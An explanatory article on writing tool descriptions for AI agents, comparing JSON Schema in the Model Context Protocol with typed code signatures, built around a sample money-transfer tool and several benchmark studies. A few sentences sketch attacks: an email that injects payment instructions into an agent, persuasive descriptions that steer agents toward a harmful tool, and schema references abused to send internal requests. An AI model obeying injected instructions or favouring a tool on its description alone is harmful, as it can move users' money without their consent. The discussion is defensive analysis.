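# Tool descriptions for AI agents: whether JSON schemas specify enough, and what typed notations add

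## What a tool description contains and who reads it

An AI agent is a software system in which a large language model decides what to do next and ordinary programs carry out the decision. The model produces only text, so to look up a bank balance, change a file or pay a bill it needs tools, which are functions that other programs offer and run. The model normally receives a tool description rather than the function's code. The description contains a name, some prose and a specification of the function's arguments, usually written in JSON Schema, a standard vocabulary for stating which JSON values are valid. JSON is the text format of nested names and values in which most web services exchange data. Kutschka and Geiger (2026), in *Notation Matters*, call it the universal exchange format of agent systems.

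A tool description may be only a dozen lines long, but it has three readers. The model uses it to choose its calls, a program uses it to reject malformed calls, and a person may have to use it to judge what the agent could do with someone's money or files. Engineers and researchers disagree on whether prose and JSON Schema can serve all three. Some would keep the format and write better descriptions. Others want a typed notation, a language that expresses an interface as types a program can check, and some of them want it to cover what a call changes in the world as well as what it accepts. Still others would set the agent's limits outside the description.

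### The agent loop

A tool call involves the model, the application that runs it (the client) and the program that offers the tool (the server). The client and server can be a single program. When they are separate, they commonly communicate through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which lets agents discover and call tools on servers.

In the current Model Context Protocol specification, *Tools* (2026), the loop starts when the client sends a `tools/list` request and the server returns its tool descriptions. The client then passes these to the model as part of the prompt. Anthropic's *Define tools* prints the template its API uses, in which a sentence announcing the available functions is followed by the definitions in JSON Schema and then the developer's own instructions. OpenAI's *Function calling* explains that OpenAI inserts the definitions into the system message, in a syntax it has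 trained the model on, and bills for them as input tokens. The model therefore receives a tool description as text, like the rest of the prompt, and a long description takes up space and costs money.

Next the model emits a call. If a user asks the agent to pay a plumber $340, the model may produce the name of a payment tool and a JSON object with the arguments. This moves no money, since the model has only written down what it wants to happen. The client turns it into a message in JSON-RPC, a convention for sending procedure calls as JSON:

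```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "transfer",
    "arguments": { "amount": 340, "payer": "ACC1001", "payee": "ACC2002" }
  }
}
```

A real request also carries metadata, such as the protocol version and the client's identity, as the Model Context Protocol's July release post (2026) shows.

A program now validates the arguments and runs the function. MCP requires servers to validate all tool inputs, so a call without a `payee` should fail here, before anything happens to an account. OpenAI's "strict mode" can handle part of this checking earlier. It makes the model's calls follow the schema reliably rather than on a best-effort basis, but it supports only some features of JSON Schema. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* distinguishes tools that run in the developer's application from tools, such as web search, that run on Anthropic's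 infrastructure.

Finally, the result goes back into the model's context, and the model either answers the user or makes another call. Some tasks need one pass through the loop, while in others, as Kutschka and Geiger describe, the model alternates between reasoning and further calls until it has a final answer. Errors also go back into the context. MCP separates protocol errors, such as an unknown tool name, from errors in executing the tool, which clients should pass to the model so that it can correct the call. The specification's example is a message that explains that a departure date must be in the future and includes today's date.

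The JSON form of this exchange dates from 13 June 2023, when OpenAI released two models fine-tuned to detect when a request needed a function and to reply with JSON that fits the function's signature. Developers described the functions in JSON Schema. The examples for human readers in OpenAI's *Function calling and other API updates* (2023) are one-line signatures such as `send_email(to: string, body: string)`, although the API itself took the longer JSON form. The developer Willison (2023) explained the same day that the model returns a description of a function call and the developer's code executes it. Most model providers have since adopted the convention. It left open how an application finds tools, and every new data source still needed its own connector. Anthropic addressed this in November 2024 with MCP, created by David Soria Parra and Justin Spahr-Summers. Anthropic's *Introducing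 the Model Context Protocol* (2024) presented it as one open standard to replace many separate integrations.

### The transfer tool in JSON

Marron (2026), in *Specifications for Humans, Agents, and Tooling*, uses a payment function as a specimen of a dangerous interface. It takes an amount, a payer and a payee, and its whole specification is one line of signature and one line of comment. Written out as an MCP tool, with more care than Marron's specimen gets, it could look like this:

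```json
{
  "name": "transfer",
  "title": "Transfer money",
  "description": "Transfer an amount from the payer's account to the payee's account. Use only when the user has asked for a payment.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "amount": {
        "type": "number",
        "exclusiveMinimum": 0,
        "description": "Amount in US dollars, e.g. 25.50"
      },
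      "payer": {
        "type": "string",
        "pattern": "^ACC[0-9]{4}$",
        "description": "Account that the money leaves"
      },
      "payee": {
        "type": "string",
        "pattern": "^ACC[0-9]{4}$",
        "description": "Account that receives the money"
      }
    },
    "required": ["amount", "payer", "payee"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  },
  "outputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
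    "properties": {
      "transfer_id": { "type": "string" },
      "status": { "type": "string", "enum": ["completed", "pending"] }
    },
    "required": ["transfer_id", "status"]
  },
  "annotations": {
    "readOnlyHint": false,
    "destructiveHint": true,
    "idempotentHint": false,
    "openWorldHint": true
  }
}
```

The model calls a tool by its `name`, which should be unique within a server. If two servers each offer a tool called `search`, the client has to tell them apart, for example with a prefix. The `title` is for display to people. The `description` is free text about what the tool does and when to use it.

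`inputSchema` holds the JSON Schema for the arguments, which must form an object, meaning a set of named values. `properties` lists the permitted names and sets a rule for each: `amount` must be a number above zero, and the two accounts must be strings that consist of the letters ACC and four digits. `required` makes all three mandatory, and `additionalProperties: false` forbids any others. A validator ignores the `description` strings inside the schema, such as "Amount in US dollars", which only the model or a person uses.

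`outputSchema` does the same for the result, which in this example is an identifier and a status with two possible values. If a tool has an output schema, the server must return results that conform to it, and the client should check that they do. Model providers' formats can cover less than MCP's. OpenAI's function definition has fields for the name, description, parameters and strict mode, but none for the result. The company advises developers to explain in words what the output represents.

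The `annotations` give four yes-or-no hints about behaviour. `readOnlyHint` is true if the tool changes nothing in its environment. `destructiveHint` separates destructive updates from purely additive ones. A payment fits this distinction badly because it adds a line to a ledger but also takes money out of an account, so a cautious author sets the hint to true. `idempotentHint` is true if repeating the same call has no further effect; it is false for `transfer`, since a second call would pay the plumber twice. `openWorldHint` indicates whether the tool interacts with outside entities. According to a March post on annotations on the Model Context Protocol (2026) blog, a client might skip the confirmation dialog for a read-only tool, warn before running a destructive one, or retry an idempotent one after a failure. Clients must not trust these hints unless they trust the server.

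MCP thus standardises the names of the fields and the messages that carry them, and leaves most of the content to the tool's author. According to Model Context Protocol's *mcp_types*, the official Python library requires only the name and the input schema; the description, output schema and annotations are optional. The specification's current revision, dated 28 July 2026, began allowing every JSON Schema 2020-12 keyword in both input and output schemas. The Model Context Protocol project has set a target date of 30 March 2027 for the next revision.

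### Type, schema, contract, effect, capability

Proposals to improve on this format draw on five terms from programming.

| Term | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Type | A class of values, with rules on how a program may use them | `amt: USD` admits a sum in dollars and refuses one in euros |
| Schema | A description of which data are valid | `"exclusiveMinimum": 0` accepts 340 and refuses −5 |
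| Contract | A statement of what must hold before a call (precondition) and what will hold after it (postcondition) | Before: the amount is within the user's payment limit. After: the payer's balance is lower by that amount |
| Effect | Anything a call does besides returning a value | `transfer` moves money; a `get_balance` tool would only return a number |
| Capability | A value that a program must hold in order to use a resource | Without the access token for account ACC1001, a program has no means of debiting it |

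Types and schemas overlap, and `"type": "number"` in the JSON above looks like both. The practical difference is that a validator applies a schema to existing data, such as the arguments of a call the model has just made, while a type checker can examine a whole program before any of it runs and find the line that passes an account number where an amount belongs.

In its narrow sense, "contract" means the two conditions in the table. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) uses the term more broadly. It presents a web agent, Baya, whose contract for each operation includes a typed signature, the prerequisites (such as a valid login, or checking the stock before adding an item to the cart) and a complete list of possible errors.

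"Capability" is the most confusing of the five terms, because MCP documents also use it for the features that a client or server supports. In the older sense, used in the table, a capability gives its holder power over a thing rather than just naming it. An account number is only a name. Anybody can type ACC1001, so the server has to check on every call whether this caller may debit that account. The MCP specification likewise says that, on a server that authenticates its callers, an identifier handed out for a shopping cart or database transaction is "a name, not a capability".

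### Three readers

Whether a description is adequate depends on its reader. The model must be able to decide from it whether the tool fits the request, and to fill each argument with the value the user means. OpenAI suggests an "intern test": could a person use the function correctly given only what the model gets? The validating program must be able to check mechanically, from the description, whether a call obeys the tool's rules. A person who reads the description before the agent starts should be able to tell what the agent could change, whose property it could affect, up to what amount, and where information could end up.

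The transfer tool's description can be adequate for any one of these readers and inadequate for another. Suppose the tool's author deletes every `description` string. The validator still accepts and rejects exactly the same calls, but the model has to guess whether `amount` is in dollars or cents. If it guesses cents, a bill of $340 becomes a valid call for $34,000. This is semantic misuse, a call that is valid under the schema but wrong for the task, as opposed to interface misuse, which breaks the declared rules for the arguments. Anthropic's guide gives a good and a poor description of a tool for stock prices that differ only in their prose, so a validator cannot tell them apart. Prose doesn't resolve every ambiguity, however. *Beyond Message Passing* (Yuan, Lyu and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 18 agent protocols, gives the example of an agent that must book a flight to "Springfield".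 The protocol delivers a well-formed message but has no mechanism for asking which Springfield. `payee` is ambiguous in the same way if a customer has two plumbers in the address book.

The opposite failure occurs when a rule appears only in the prose. *Improving tool-call reliability with JSON Schema 2020-12* (Caldeira, 2026) demonstrates this with a bank that requires an approval code for transfers above $10,000. In one version, the parameter descriptions mentioned the rule but the schema did not enforce it. A call for $12,500 without a code passed validation, and the bank's ledger refused it. The agent received only the message "transfer rejected", which could equally have meant insufficient funds, and did not try to fix the call. In the other version, the schema contained the rule. The server's validator stopped the call and named the missing field, and the agent copied the code from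 the user's prompt and succeeded on the second try. Caldeira left the code out of the first call on purpose, because a capable model often supplies it unprompted, so the demonstration gives little evidence of how often models need such help. It does show that leaving a rule out of the schema can also hurt the model, which may then receive an error message too vague to act on.

The description serves the person worst. The JSON above is careful by current standards, but it sets no upper limit on the amount, accepts any correctly formatted account number as the payer, and doesn't state whose authority the server acts on. Marron warns that nothing in the same function's specification rules out that it also uploads the user's account details to an attacker. The annotations don't help, because all four have the values that MCP assumes for a tool with no annotations, and a tool that wipes a disk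 could have the same four. In March 2026, according to the Model Context Protocol blog, no MCP client displayed annotations in its approval prompts.

MCP's main provision for the person comes later, during the run, when applications should show a call's arguments before sending it and let a human deny it. In 2023, OpenAI similarly recommended asking users for confirmation before an agent sends an email or makes a purchase. A dialog that reads "$340 from ACC1001 to ACC2002" is much easier to judge than a schema, but it covers only one call and appears after the agent already has the tool. A pre-run review has to cover the environment, meaning all the tools, data and permissions the agent holds for the run, because the risk depends on how they combine. For example, the descriptions of a payment tool and an email tool don't mention each other, but if an agent has both, a stranger's email may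 contain instructions to pay somebody, and the model cannot reliably tell these from the user's own.

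## The case for keeping JSON Schema and writing better descriptions

The transfer tool's author could fix most of its faults and still use JSON. The keyword `maximum` would cap the amount. An `enum`, a list of permitted values, could restrict the payer to the user's own accounts, since the Model Context Protocol specification lets a server offer different tools to callers with different permissions. A few more sentences in the description could explain whose credentials the server uses and when the agent should ask before paying. On this view, JSON Schema serves all three readers well enough, and the problem is how people fill it in.

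JSON Schema is already widely used. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports that MCP's software libraries are downloaded more than 400 million times a month, a fourfold increase within the year. OpenAPI, the usual standard for describing web services, uses the same schema language, so a company that has documented its services properly has already written much of what an agent needs. Caldeira advises such companies to treat those existing definitions as the source of truth and to stop restating their rules in prose. A new notation would have to win over tool authors, client developers and the companies that train models.

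A richer language would also have to be worth the effort. If most bad calls happen because the tool's author left something out, it may not help much, since someone who hasn't explained a parameter in English is unlikely to write a formal contract for it.

### Writing for a new hire

Anthropic's *Writing effective tools for agents* takes this position. It advises developers to describe a tool as they would to a new colleague, including what they normally take for granted, such as special query formats, the meaning of niche terms and how the underlying resources relate to each other. It recommends unambiguous parameter names, for example `user_id` instead of `user`. It also recommends combining these descriptions with strict data models that enforce the expected inputs and outputs.

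Anthropic wants developers to test descriptions like any other part of the software. They write realistic tasks, some of which need dozens of tool calls, run an agent on them and read the transcripts for signs of confusion. Many invalid-parameter errors suggest that the descriptions need to be clearer or need better examples. When Anthropic launched web search for its model Claude, it found that the model was needlessly adding "2025" to its queries, which skewed the results. It fixed this by editing the tool's description. Validation would not have caught the problem, because a query containing a year is a valid string.

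Anthropic also has Claude rewrite tools. On tasks not used in the rewriting, Claude's versions of the company's internal tools did better than the versions its researchers had written. This is only weak evidence for better descriptions, since Claude could also change a tool's code. Anthropic says small refinements to tool descriptions helped Claude Sonnet 3.5, now an old model, reach a record score on SWE-bench Verified, a test of fixing real software bugs, but it doesn't say how much they contributed.

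### What the July 2026 release allows

Until July 2026, MCP used only part of JSON Schema. The protocol had adopted the 2020-12 version of the standard after Hungerford (2025) proposed it in *Establish JSON Schema 2020-12 as Default Dialect for MCP*. But MCP's definition of an input schema allowed only three top-level fields: `type`, `properties` and `required`. An author could constrain each argument in detail, but the schema had no place for a rule that connected two arguments, so such rules had to go in the prose or in the server's code.

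McBride and Hungerford (2026), in *Tools inputSchema & outputSchema Conform to JSON Schema 2020-12*, proposed lifting the restriction, and the July release did so. In its announcement of the release candidate, Model Context Protocol (2026) called the release the largest revision since the protocol's launch. The schema for the transfer tool can now contain conditional rules, such as the one from Caldeira's bank demonstration that a transfer above $10,000 needs an approval code:

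```json
"if": {
  "required": ["amount"],
  "properties": { "amount": { "exclusiveMinimum": 10000 } }
},
"then": { "required": ["approval_code"] }
```

Another new option, `oneOf`, requires a call to match exactly one of several sub-schemas. McBride and Hungerford describe a lookup tool that accepts either an identifier or a name. A call with both fails because it matches both sub-schemas. Caldeira uses `oneOf` to separate transfers within the bank, which need an account number, from wire transfers, which need international bank codes, so that a model can't mix the two. `$defs` and `$ref` let an author define the account number format once and refer to it wherever it occurs.

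These combinations can also cause errors. The transfer tool's `additionalProperties: false` allows only the properties listed right beside it, so it would reject arguments declared in a `oneOf` branch. Caldeira's schema uses `unevaluatedProperties: false`, which also allows properties declared in the matching `oneOf` branch.

The rules for results loosened even more. An output schema previously had to describe an object, so a weather tool had to wrap a list of hourly forecasts in an object before returning it. FastMCP, a popular Python library for building MCP servers, had to add its own code to wrap results. McBride and Hungerford cite a bug in which schemas of an unexpected form broke every tool on a server. They also point to OpenAPI, which began with a modified subset of JSON Schema and later accepted breaking changes to adopt the full 2020-12 version. Both cases support keeping JSON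 Schema, since the trouble came from restrictions that the protocols had added to it.

The larger vocabulary creates some problems. A `$ref` may contain a web address. If a program fetched it automatically, an attacker could use a tool definition to send requests from inside a company's network, so the specification forbids automatic fetching. Some combinations of keywords take a long time to check, so implementations should limit schema depth and validation time. Older clients may not handle an input schema that goes beyond the original three fields.

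### How strict modes work

A strict mode usually relies on constrained decoding, which stops the model from writing a malformed call. A language model produces text one token (a word or a fragment of one) at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software running it picks one. With constrained decoding, the software first converts the schema into a grammar that defines which continuations are allowed. Before each pick, it sets the probability of every token that would break the grammar to zero. Once the model has written `"payer": "ACC`, for example, only tokens that begin with a digit remain, and the model still chooses which digit.

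Constrained decoding rules out interface misuse in any call the model completes, but only for the schema constraints that the engine supports. It does not prevent semantic misuse, such as entering $34,000 instead of $340, because both amounts fit the schema.

The constraint can even hide a problem. Suppose the user hasn't said which account belongs to the plumber. Without the constraint, the model might leave out `payee`, and the validator would return an error naming the missing field. With it, a model that has started the call must fill in `payee` with something that looks like an account number. Approval codes carry a similar risk. Caldeira's demonstration schema fixes the code as a published constant, so an engine that enforced the whole schema would insert the code into every large transfer, whether or not anyone had approved it. Caldeira calls the constant a placeholder and says a production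 server should verify approval itself and keep the value out of the schema.

### How much authors leave out

A good deal of evidence supports the claim that authors are to blame. In *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Tool Descriptions Are Smelly!*, Hasan, Li and colleagues (2026) collected 856 tools from 103 MCP servers. Three language models from different developers scored each tool's description from 1 to 5 on six components: purpose, guidelines for use, limitations, explanation of parameters, length and completeness, and examples. An average below 3 on a component counted as a "smell", the programmers' term for a sign of poor quality.

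At least one smell appeared in 97.1% of the descriptions. Limitations were missing or inadequate in 89.8%, guidelines for use in 89.3% and explanations of parameters in 84.3%. The 97.1% figure reflects a demanding rubric, since a description must meet every criterion to count as clean, and a simple tool may have few limitations to report. But 56% did not even make the tool's purpose clear. An official tool for creating PayPal invoices had only the description "Creates PayPal Invoice Link." The 23 servers maintained by companies and other organisations did not score significantly better than the 80 from the open-source community.

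These scores measure how much a description covers, but a full description can still be false. *From Docs to Descriptions* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) therefore compares descriptions with code. It pairs tool descriptions from 10,831 MCP servers with the code behind each tool, and uses gpt-4o-mini to find mismatches and omissions and group them as it went, which produced 18 kinds of flaw. The most common, with 7,894 cases, was a tool name that also occurs elsewhere, which is fairly mild because clients can add prefixes. More serious were 3,572 confusing accounts of what a tool does, 3,449 wrong explanations of a parameter, 3,093 missing descriptions of the return value and 2,972 cases with no guidance on when to use the tool. For a person who has to approve a tool, the worst flaws are probably the 931 cases of undeclared behaviour and the 773 cases of omitted side effects.

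Neither study gives precise rates. Hasan and colleagues found that guidance on when to use a tool was missing or inadequate in 89% of their sample, while Wang and colleagues' count works out to about 27% of theirs. The studies used different samples and criteria, and both used language models as judges. Wang and colleagues collected their servers in March 2025, when MCP was a few months old.

Flaws like these change which tools a model picks. In a second experiment, Wang and colleagues wrote good and poor descriptions for ten kinds of server, replaced the tools' names with random identifiers, and sent gpt-4o-mini 1,000 requests. The model picked a tool 17.8% of the time when the description explained its function well and 6.2% when it explained it poorly. The figures were 15.9% and 7.1% for good and poor accuracy, and 14.3% and 8.4% for good and poor completeness. Conciseness made little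 difference.

### What longer descriptions gain and cost

If omissions cause failures, adding the missing information should help. Hasan and colleagues tested this on MCP-Universe, a benchmark of 231 tasks in six areas, such as finance, navigation and web search, with results checked by programs. They had GPT-4.1-mini expand the benchmark's tool descriptions. To keep it from inventing examples and limitations, they first ran the tools on hand-written tasks, including some meant to fail, and gave it the logs.

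| Agent's model | Tasks solved, original descriptions | Tasks solved, expanded | Average steps, original | Average steps, expanded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 18.2% | 29.4% | 5.2 | 8.1 |
| Qwen3-Coder | 19.9% | 26.0% | 7.8 | 14.1 |
| GLM-4.5 | 24.7% | 25.3% | 7.3 | 14.8 |
| Qwen3-Next | 15.6% | 21.2% | 9.5 | 7.0 |

The median gain was 5.85 percentage points, but the median number of steps rose 67%, which means more calls to the model and a higher bill. Of the 24 combinations of model and subject area, 13 improved and four got worse. Qwen3-Coder rose from 40% to 72.5% on finance tasks, while GLM-4.5 fell from 27% to 18% on web search.

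To save money, the team took the original scores for the first three models from the benchmark's own paper rather than rerunning them, and it used a different search tool for the web tasks. Some of the differences may therefore come from the set-up. The Qwen3-Next comparison is the most reliable because the team ran both versions itself. This model has less room for text, so its descriptions were shorter and covered only purpose, guidelines and limitations. With them, it solved more tasks and took fewer steps on average, but the paper also reports that about three quarters of its tasks took more steps than before. Both can be true only if a few very long runs became much shorter, so it remains unclear how much extra work longer descriptions cause.

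More text isn't always better. GPT-4.1 solved 67.5% of the finance tasks with only the purpose and guidelines, compared with 57.5% with the full descriptions. One reason was that the rewriting model had added a confusing limitation to a stock-price tool's description, which mentioned a contradiction without resolving it. The useful guidelines for the same tool included advice to set the end date one day after the last day needed, because the tool excludes the end date. Leaving out the examples made no significant difference. Since no combination of components was best everywhere, Hasan and colleagues suggest that MCP should split its single `description` string into separate fields, still in JSON, so that a client can load only what it needs.

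### A model that rewrites descriptions

Running every tool to find out what its description lacks is slow, and it is dangerous when a tool moves money. In *Learning to Rewrite Tool Descriptions for Reliable LLM-Agent Tool Use*, Guo, Dong and colleagues (2026) trained a model that improves descriptions without running the tools. Their method, Trace-Free+, writes a new description from a tool's existing description and schema, and leaves the schema unchanged.

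Guo and colleagues used 991 tools from real web services for training and kept 4,585 others for testing. They generated requests that needed several of the training tools in sequence, let an agent attempt them, and recorded its successes and failures. They then improved each description in two rounds, first by applying general documentation guidelines and then by adding rules drawn from the failures. They trained a small model, Qwen3-4B, to reproduce the improved descriptions. Most examples early in training included a summary of the recorded runs, but most later ones did not, so the model had to infer the same information from the description and schema alone.

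With GPT-4.1 as the agent, the new descriptions raised success on multi-step requests in the StableToolBench benchmark from 33.5% to 44.6%. The test supplied the correct intermediate result after every step, so an early mistake did not affect later steps. On tools from services the rewriter had never seen, success rose from 49.5% to 74.9% for a film database and from 34.9% to 49.3% for Spotify. The advantage grew when the agent had to choose among 150 additional tools. On BFCLv2, a benchmark that checks the form of function calls without running them, the improvement was much smaller, at 1.4 points for Gemini 3 Pro and 2.4 for Claude Sonnet 4.5.

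A comparison with a small agent model supports the view that the descriptions are the weak point. Training the agent on the 991 tools raised its success rate on the film and music services only from 54.1% to 55.0%, while giving the untrained agent better descriptions raised it to 62.1%.

Guo and colleagues also counted what the descriptions of media and finance tools contained before and after rewriting:

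| The description states | Original | Rewritten by guidelines only | Trace-Free+ |
|---|---|---|---|
| When to use the tool, or when not to | 3.3% | 99.7% | 97.2% |
| Which other tool must supply a value | 0.3% | 32.0% | 30.0% |
| What the result contains | 11.6% | 98.6% | 27.0% |
| Which values a parameter accepts | 9.9% | 87.9% | 94.2% |
| How one parameter restricts another | 0.3% | 8.5% | 17.1% |

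The originals contained almost nothing that an agent needs to choose between tools. The middle column supports keeping JSON Schema, because those rewrites took no special training, only a language model with a list of what good documentation should contain. On requests that needed a single call, agents succeeded 61.6% of the time with these simpler rewrites, 60.7% with Trace-Free+ and 59.2% with the original descriptions, so most of the benefit comes in longer tasks.

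### What rewriting cannot repair

After either kind of rewriting, about 70% of the descriptions still don't name any other tool that has to run first. Some of those tools surely need nothing from any other, but Guo and colleagues don't report how many, so we don't know what share of dependencies is still missing. Gaps are likely because the rewriter sees one tool at a time and is instructed not to mention tools it hasn't been given. The developer of an MCP server is in much the same position with other people's servers. Anthropic suggests merging tools that agents often use in sequence. For example, a `schedule_event` tool that finds a free slot and books it leaves no dependency to describe. This works only if one developer controls all the steps.

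The rewritten text is also still prose, so a program cannot check it. One of the test tools returns a "Walk Score", a rating of how easy it is to get around a place on foot. Part of its original description had apparently been copied from a film database, since it offered "movie, series, episode" as formats for the result. Trace-Free+ replaced this with sensible rules, such as that the `bike` option must be exactly `1`. In the description, that rule is only advice to the model, but an author could express it as an `enum`, which the server would then enforce.

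A program also can't tell whether the advice is right. The original Walk Score description asked for a URL-encoded address, with spaces and special characters replaced by codes. The rewritten one says the address must not be URL-encoded. Guo and colleagues list this as a correction, but the rewriter had never called the service. They acknowledge that it may invent limits that a server doesn't impose, and they did not measure how often this happens. An invented limit is hard to notice because an agent that follows it never makes the call, so no error appears.

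Moving every rule into the schema would let a validator check calls against those rules, but the schema itself can be wrong. Before their experiments, Guo and colleagues had to correct schemas in StableToolBench that omitted required parameters, listed unsupported ones or gave the wrong types. They found the errors by calling the tools and reading the servers' replies. A validator can't detect such errors because it compares calls only with the schema, not with the program behind it. Some facts about a tool also can't be expressed in any schema.

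Models are more likely to choose a tool with a well-written description, whether or not the description is accurate. Wang and colleagues took ten groups of five equivalent real servers and rewrote one description in each group to meet their standard. The model chose the server with the rewritten description 72% of the time, compared with 20% by chance. The servers in each group did the same job, so the agent gained nothing from this preference. A dishonest author could use the same technique to draw calls to a harmful tool.

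## The case for giving agents program signatures instead of JSON tools

Some engineers would keep MCP servers and their schemas but stop showing the schemas to the model. Cloudflare converts the schemas into function signatures, short declarations that show how to call a function, and the model writes a small program that calls the functions. Cloudflare calls this Code Mode, and the general term is programmatic tool calling. The idea comes from CodeAct, a 2024 agent design in which the model acted by writing Python. Anthropic and OpenAI now have their own versions, and OpenAI supports it in GPT-6.

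### Real code and contrived tool calls

In *Code Mode*, Varda and Pai argue that models handle code better than tool calls because they have seen much more of it in training. A model marks a tool call with special tokens that never occur in ordinary text, so its developers have to teach it the format with synthetic examples, whereas it has seen code from millions of open-source projects. Varda and Pai compare tool calling to giving Shakespeare a month of Mandarin lessons and then asking him to write a play in Mandarin. They add that designers of MCP servers simplify their tools because models struggle with complicated ones, although models that write code work well with the full interfaces made for human developers.

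Their other argument is that a program can carry out a task with several steps without passing every result through the model. In the usual loop, the model receives the result of each call and copies the values it needs into the next one. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* gives the example of checking whether 20 employees have kept to their budgets. With ordinary calls, this takes 20 round trips and fills the model's context with thousands of expense items. A single script can do all 20 lookups and return only the employees who overspent.

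If the first argument is right, signatures should help even with a single call. The second argument is about running code, so it would hold whatever notation the model was trained on. Varda and Pai published no measurements that would distinguish the two effects.

### The transfer tool as a program

When an agent connects to an MCP server, Cloudflare's software fetches the tool descriptions and generates declarations in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types. For the transfer tool, the result would look roughly like this:

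```ts
type TransferInput = {
  /** Amount in US dollars, e.g. 25.50 */
  amount: number;
  /** Account that the money leaves */
  payer: string;
  /** Account that receives the money */
  payee: string;
};
type TransferOutput = {
  transfer_id: string;
  status: "completed" | "pending";
};
declare const bank: {
  /** Transfer an amount from the payer's account to the payee's
      account. Use only when the user has asked for a payment. */
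  transfer(input: TransferInput): Promise<TransferOutput>;
};
```

This takes 17 lines, compared with 41 in JSON, but it is shorter partly because it leaves information out. TypeScript's `number` includes negative numbers and its `string` accepts any text, so the lower limit on the amount and the format of the account numbers can only be written as comments. The signature has no place for the four annotations. It can't express the bank's rule about approval codes either, because a TypeScript type cannot compare an amount with $10,000. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode API reference*, the converter turns any schema it doesn't support into `unknown`, which carries no information.

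In the current set-up, the model doesn't receive all the signatures at the start. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* explains that it sees one tool, which accepts a piece of code, and a list of the connected services. It can use a first script to search for suitable functions and request their signatures, and a second to call them. If the bank also offers a `get_balance` tool, the script for the plumber's bill might be:

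```js
async () => {
  const account = await bank.get_balance({ account: "ACC1001" });
  if (account.balance < 340) {
    return { paid: false, balance: account.balance };
  }
  return await bank.transfer({
    amount: 340, payer: "ACC1001", payee: "ACC2002"
  });
}
```

The script runs in a sandbox that starts within milliseconds and blocks internet access by default. It can reach the bank only through the `bank` object, which makes that object a capability in the older, security sense of the word. When the script calls the object, a supervising program outside the sandbox adds the access token and sends the server an ordinary MCP request. The script never holds the token, so it cannot leak it. The result comes back to the script, and the model sees only what the script finally returns.

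The server therefore still validates calls against JSON Schema, and the signatures are there for the model to read. The model writes plain JavaScript, and the sandbox runs it without checking it against the declared types. A script that passes the text `"340"` where a number is required fails only when the call reaches a validator. In Anthropic's version, tools that scripts can call also lose the existing safeguard of strict mode, which they don't support.

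A developer can make `transfer` require approval. When a script calls it, Cloudflare's runtime stops the script, and the application can show the user the pending call with its arguments. After approval, the runtime reruns the script from the top, using recorded results for calls that have already finished. If the script requests a payment in the morning and the user approves it in the evening, the rerun still uses the morning's balance unless the developer has set `get_balance` to run again.

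OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* is more cautious. It recommends scripts for gathering and filtering data, but direct calls by default for anything that writes data or needs approval, "to preserve a clear authorization boundary". Under that advice, a script could look up the balance, but `transfer` would remain an ordinary JSON call.

### Fourteen models on 309 requests

*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compares JSON calls with programs most directly. The team took 309 requests from BFCL v4, a later version of the benchmark on which Guo and colleagues' rewritten descriptions helped only a little. Each of 14 models answered the requests once with JSON calls and once with a Python script. For the scripts, the team compiled the benchmark's schemas into stubs, which are functions with a typed signature and almost no body. An answer counted as correct only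 if it contained every required call with the right arguments. A separate set of 52 requests tested chains of 2 to 20 calls, in which one call's result feeds the next.

| Model | Main test, JSON | Main test, code | Chains, JSON | Chains, code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 81.9% | 85.8% | 88.5% | 73.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 86.4% | 87.7% | 90.4% | 88.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 80.9% | 87.4% | 90.4% | 92.3% |
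| Claude Opus 4.8 | 84.8% | 84.8% | 80.8% | 94.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 84.5% | 86.1% | 80.8% | 96.2% |
| GPT-4o | 81.9% | 55.0% | 92.3% | 86.5% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.9% | 62.1% | 98.1% | 40.4% |
| GPT-5-nano | 66.7% | 68.3% | 69.2% | 80.8% |
| GPT-5 | 71.5% | 76.1% | 92.3% | 92.3% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 79.3% | 55.0% | 76.9% | 80.8% |
| GPT-5.4 | 79.3% | 81.9% | 94.2% | 90.4% |
| GPT-5.6-Luna | 76.1% | 80.3% | 82.7% | 92.3% |
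| GPT-5.6-Sol | 72.2% | 82.8% | 96.2% | 90.4% |
| GPT-5.6-Terra | 73.5% | 84.1% | 98.1% | 96.2% |

In the main test, code matched or beat JSON for 11 of the 14 models. The average still fell slightly, from 78.6% with JSON to 77.0% with code, because GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini did so badly. Despite a warning in the prompt, those three wrote the characters `\n` where the script needed a line break, so every script longer than a line crashed. Across the other 11 models, the average rose from 78.0% to 82.3%. Patel and colleagues conclude that success with code depends on a model's generation, but GPT-5.4-mini, from March 2026, made this mistake even though the older GPT-5-nano, from August 2025, did not.

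The GPT-5.6 models' gains also look less impressive when compared with older models' scores. With code, GPT-5.6-Sol reached 82.8%, barely more than GPT-4o's 81.9% with JSON. Its 10.6-point improvement is therefore due in good part to a weak JSON score.

On chains, code matched or beat JSON for only 7 of the 14 models. Patel and colleagues write that all the Anthropic models did as well or better with code in every test, but in their results Claude Haiku 4.5 lost 15 points on chains. They report an advantage of 18.8 points for code on chains of 12 or more calls, though the set has only ten chains longer than that. The clearer benefit was speed, as 13 models finished the chains faster with code, most in about half the time, because they didn't have to stop and read each result.

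Code did worse than JSON on requests for several independent calls. The average fell from 85.5% with JSON to 71.4% with code on the benchmark's own parallel requests, and from 66.1% to 56.8% on those collected from real users, partly because of the line-break fault. In an extra test with 7 to 48 calls per request, ten models scored 100% with both formats, and GPT-5 improved from 71.9% with JSON to 96.9% with code. Claude Sonnet 5 issued all the required JSON calls for requests of up to 70, but failed every time at 100, which it could handle with a script. GPT-5.6-Sol managed 100 in JSON too, so this limit doesn't apply to every model. Scripts used fewer tokens than JSON only above about 26 calls.

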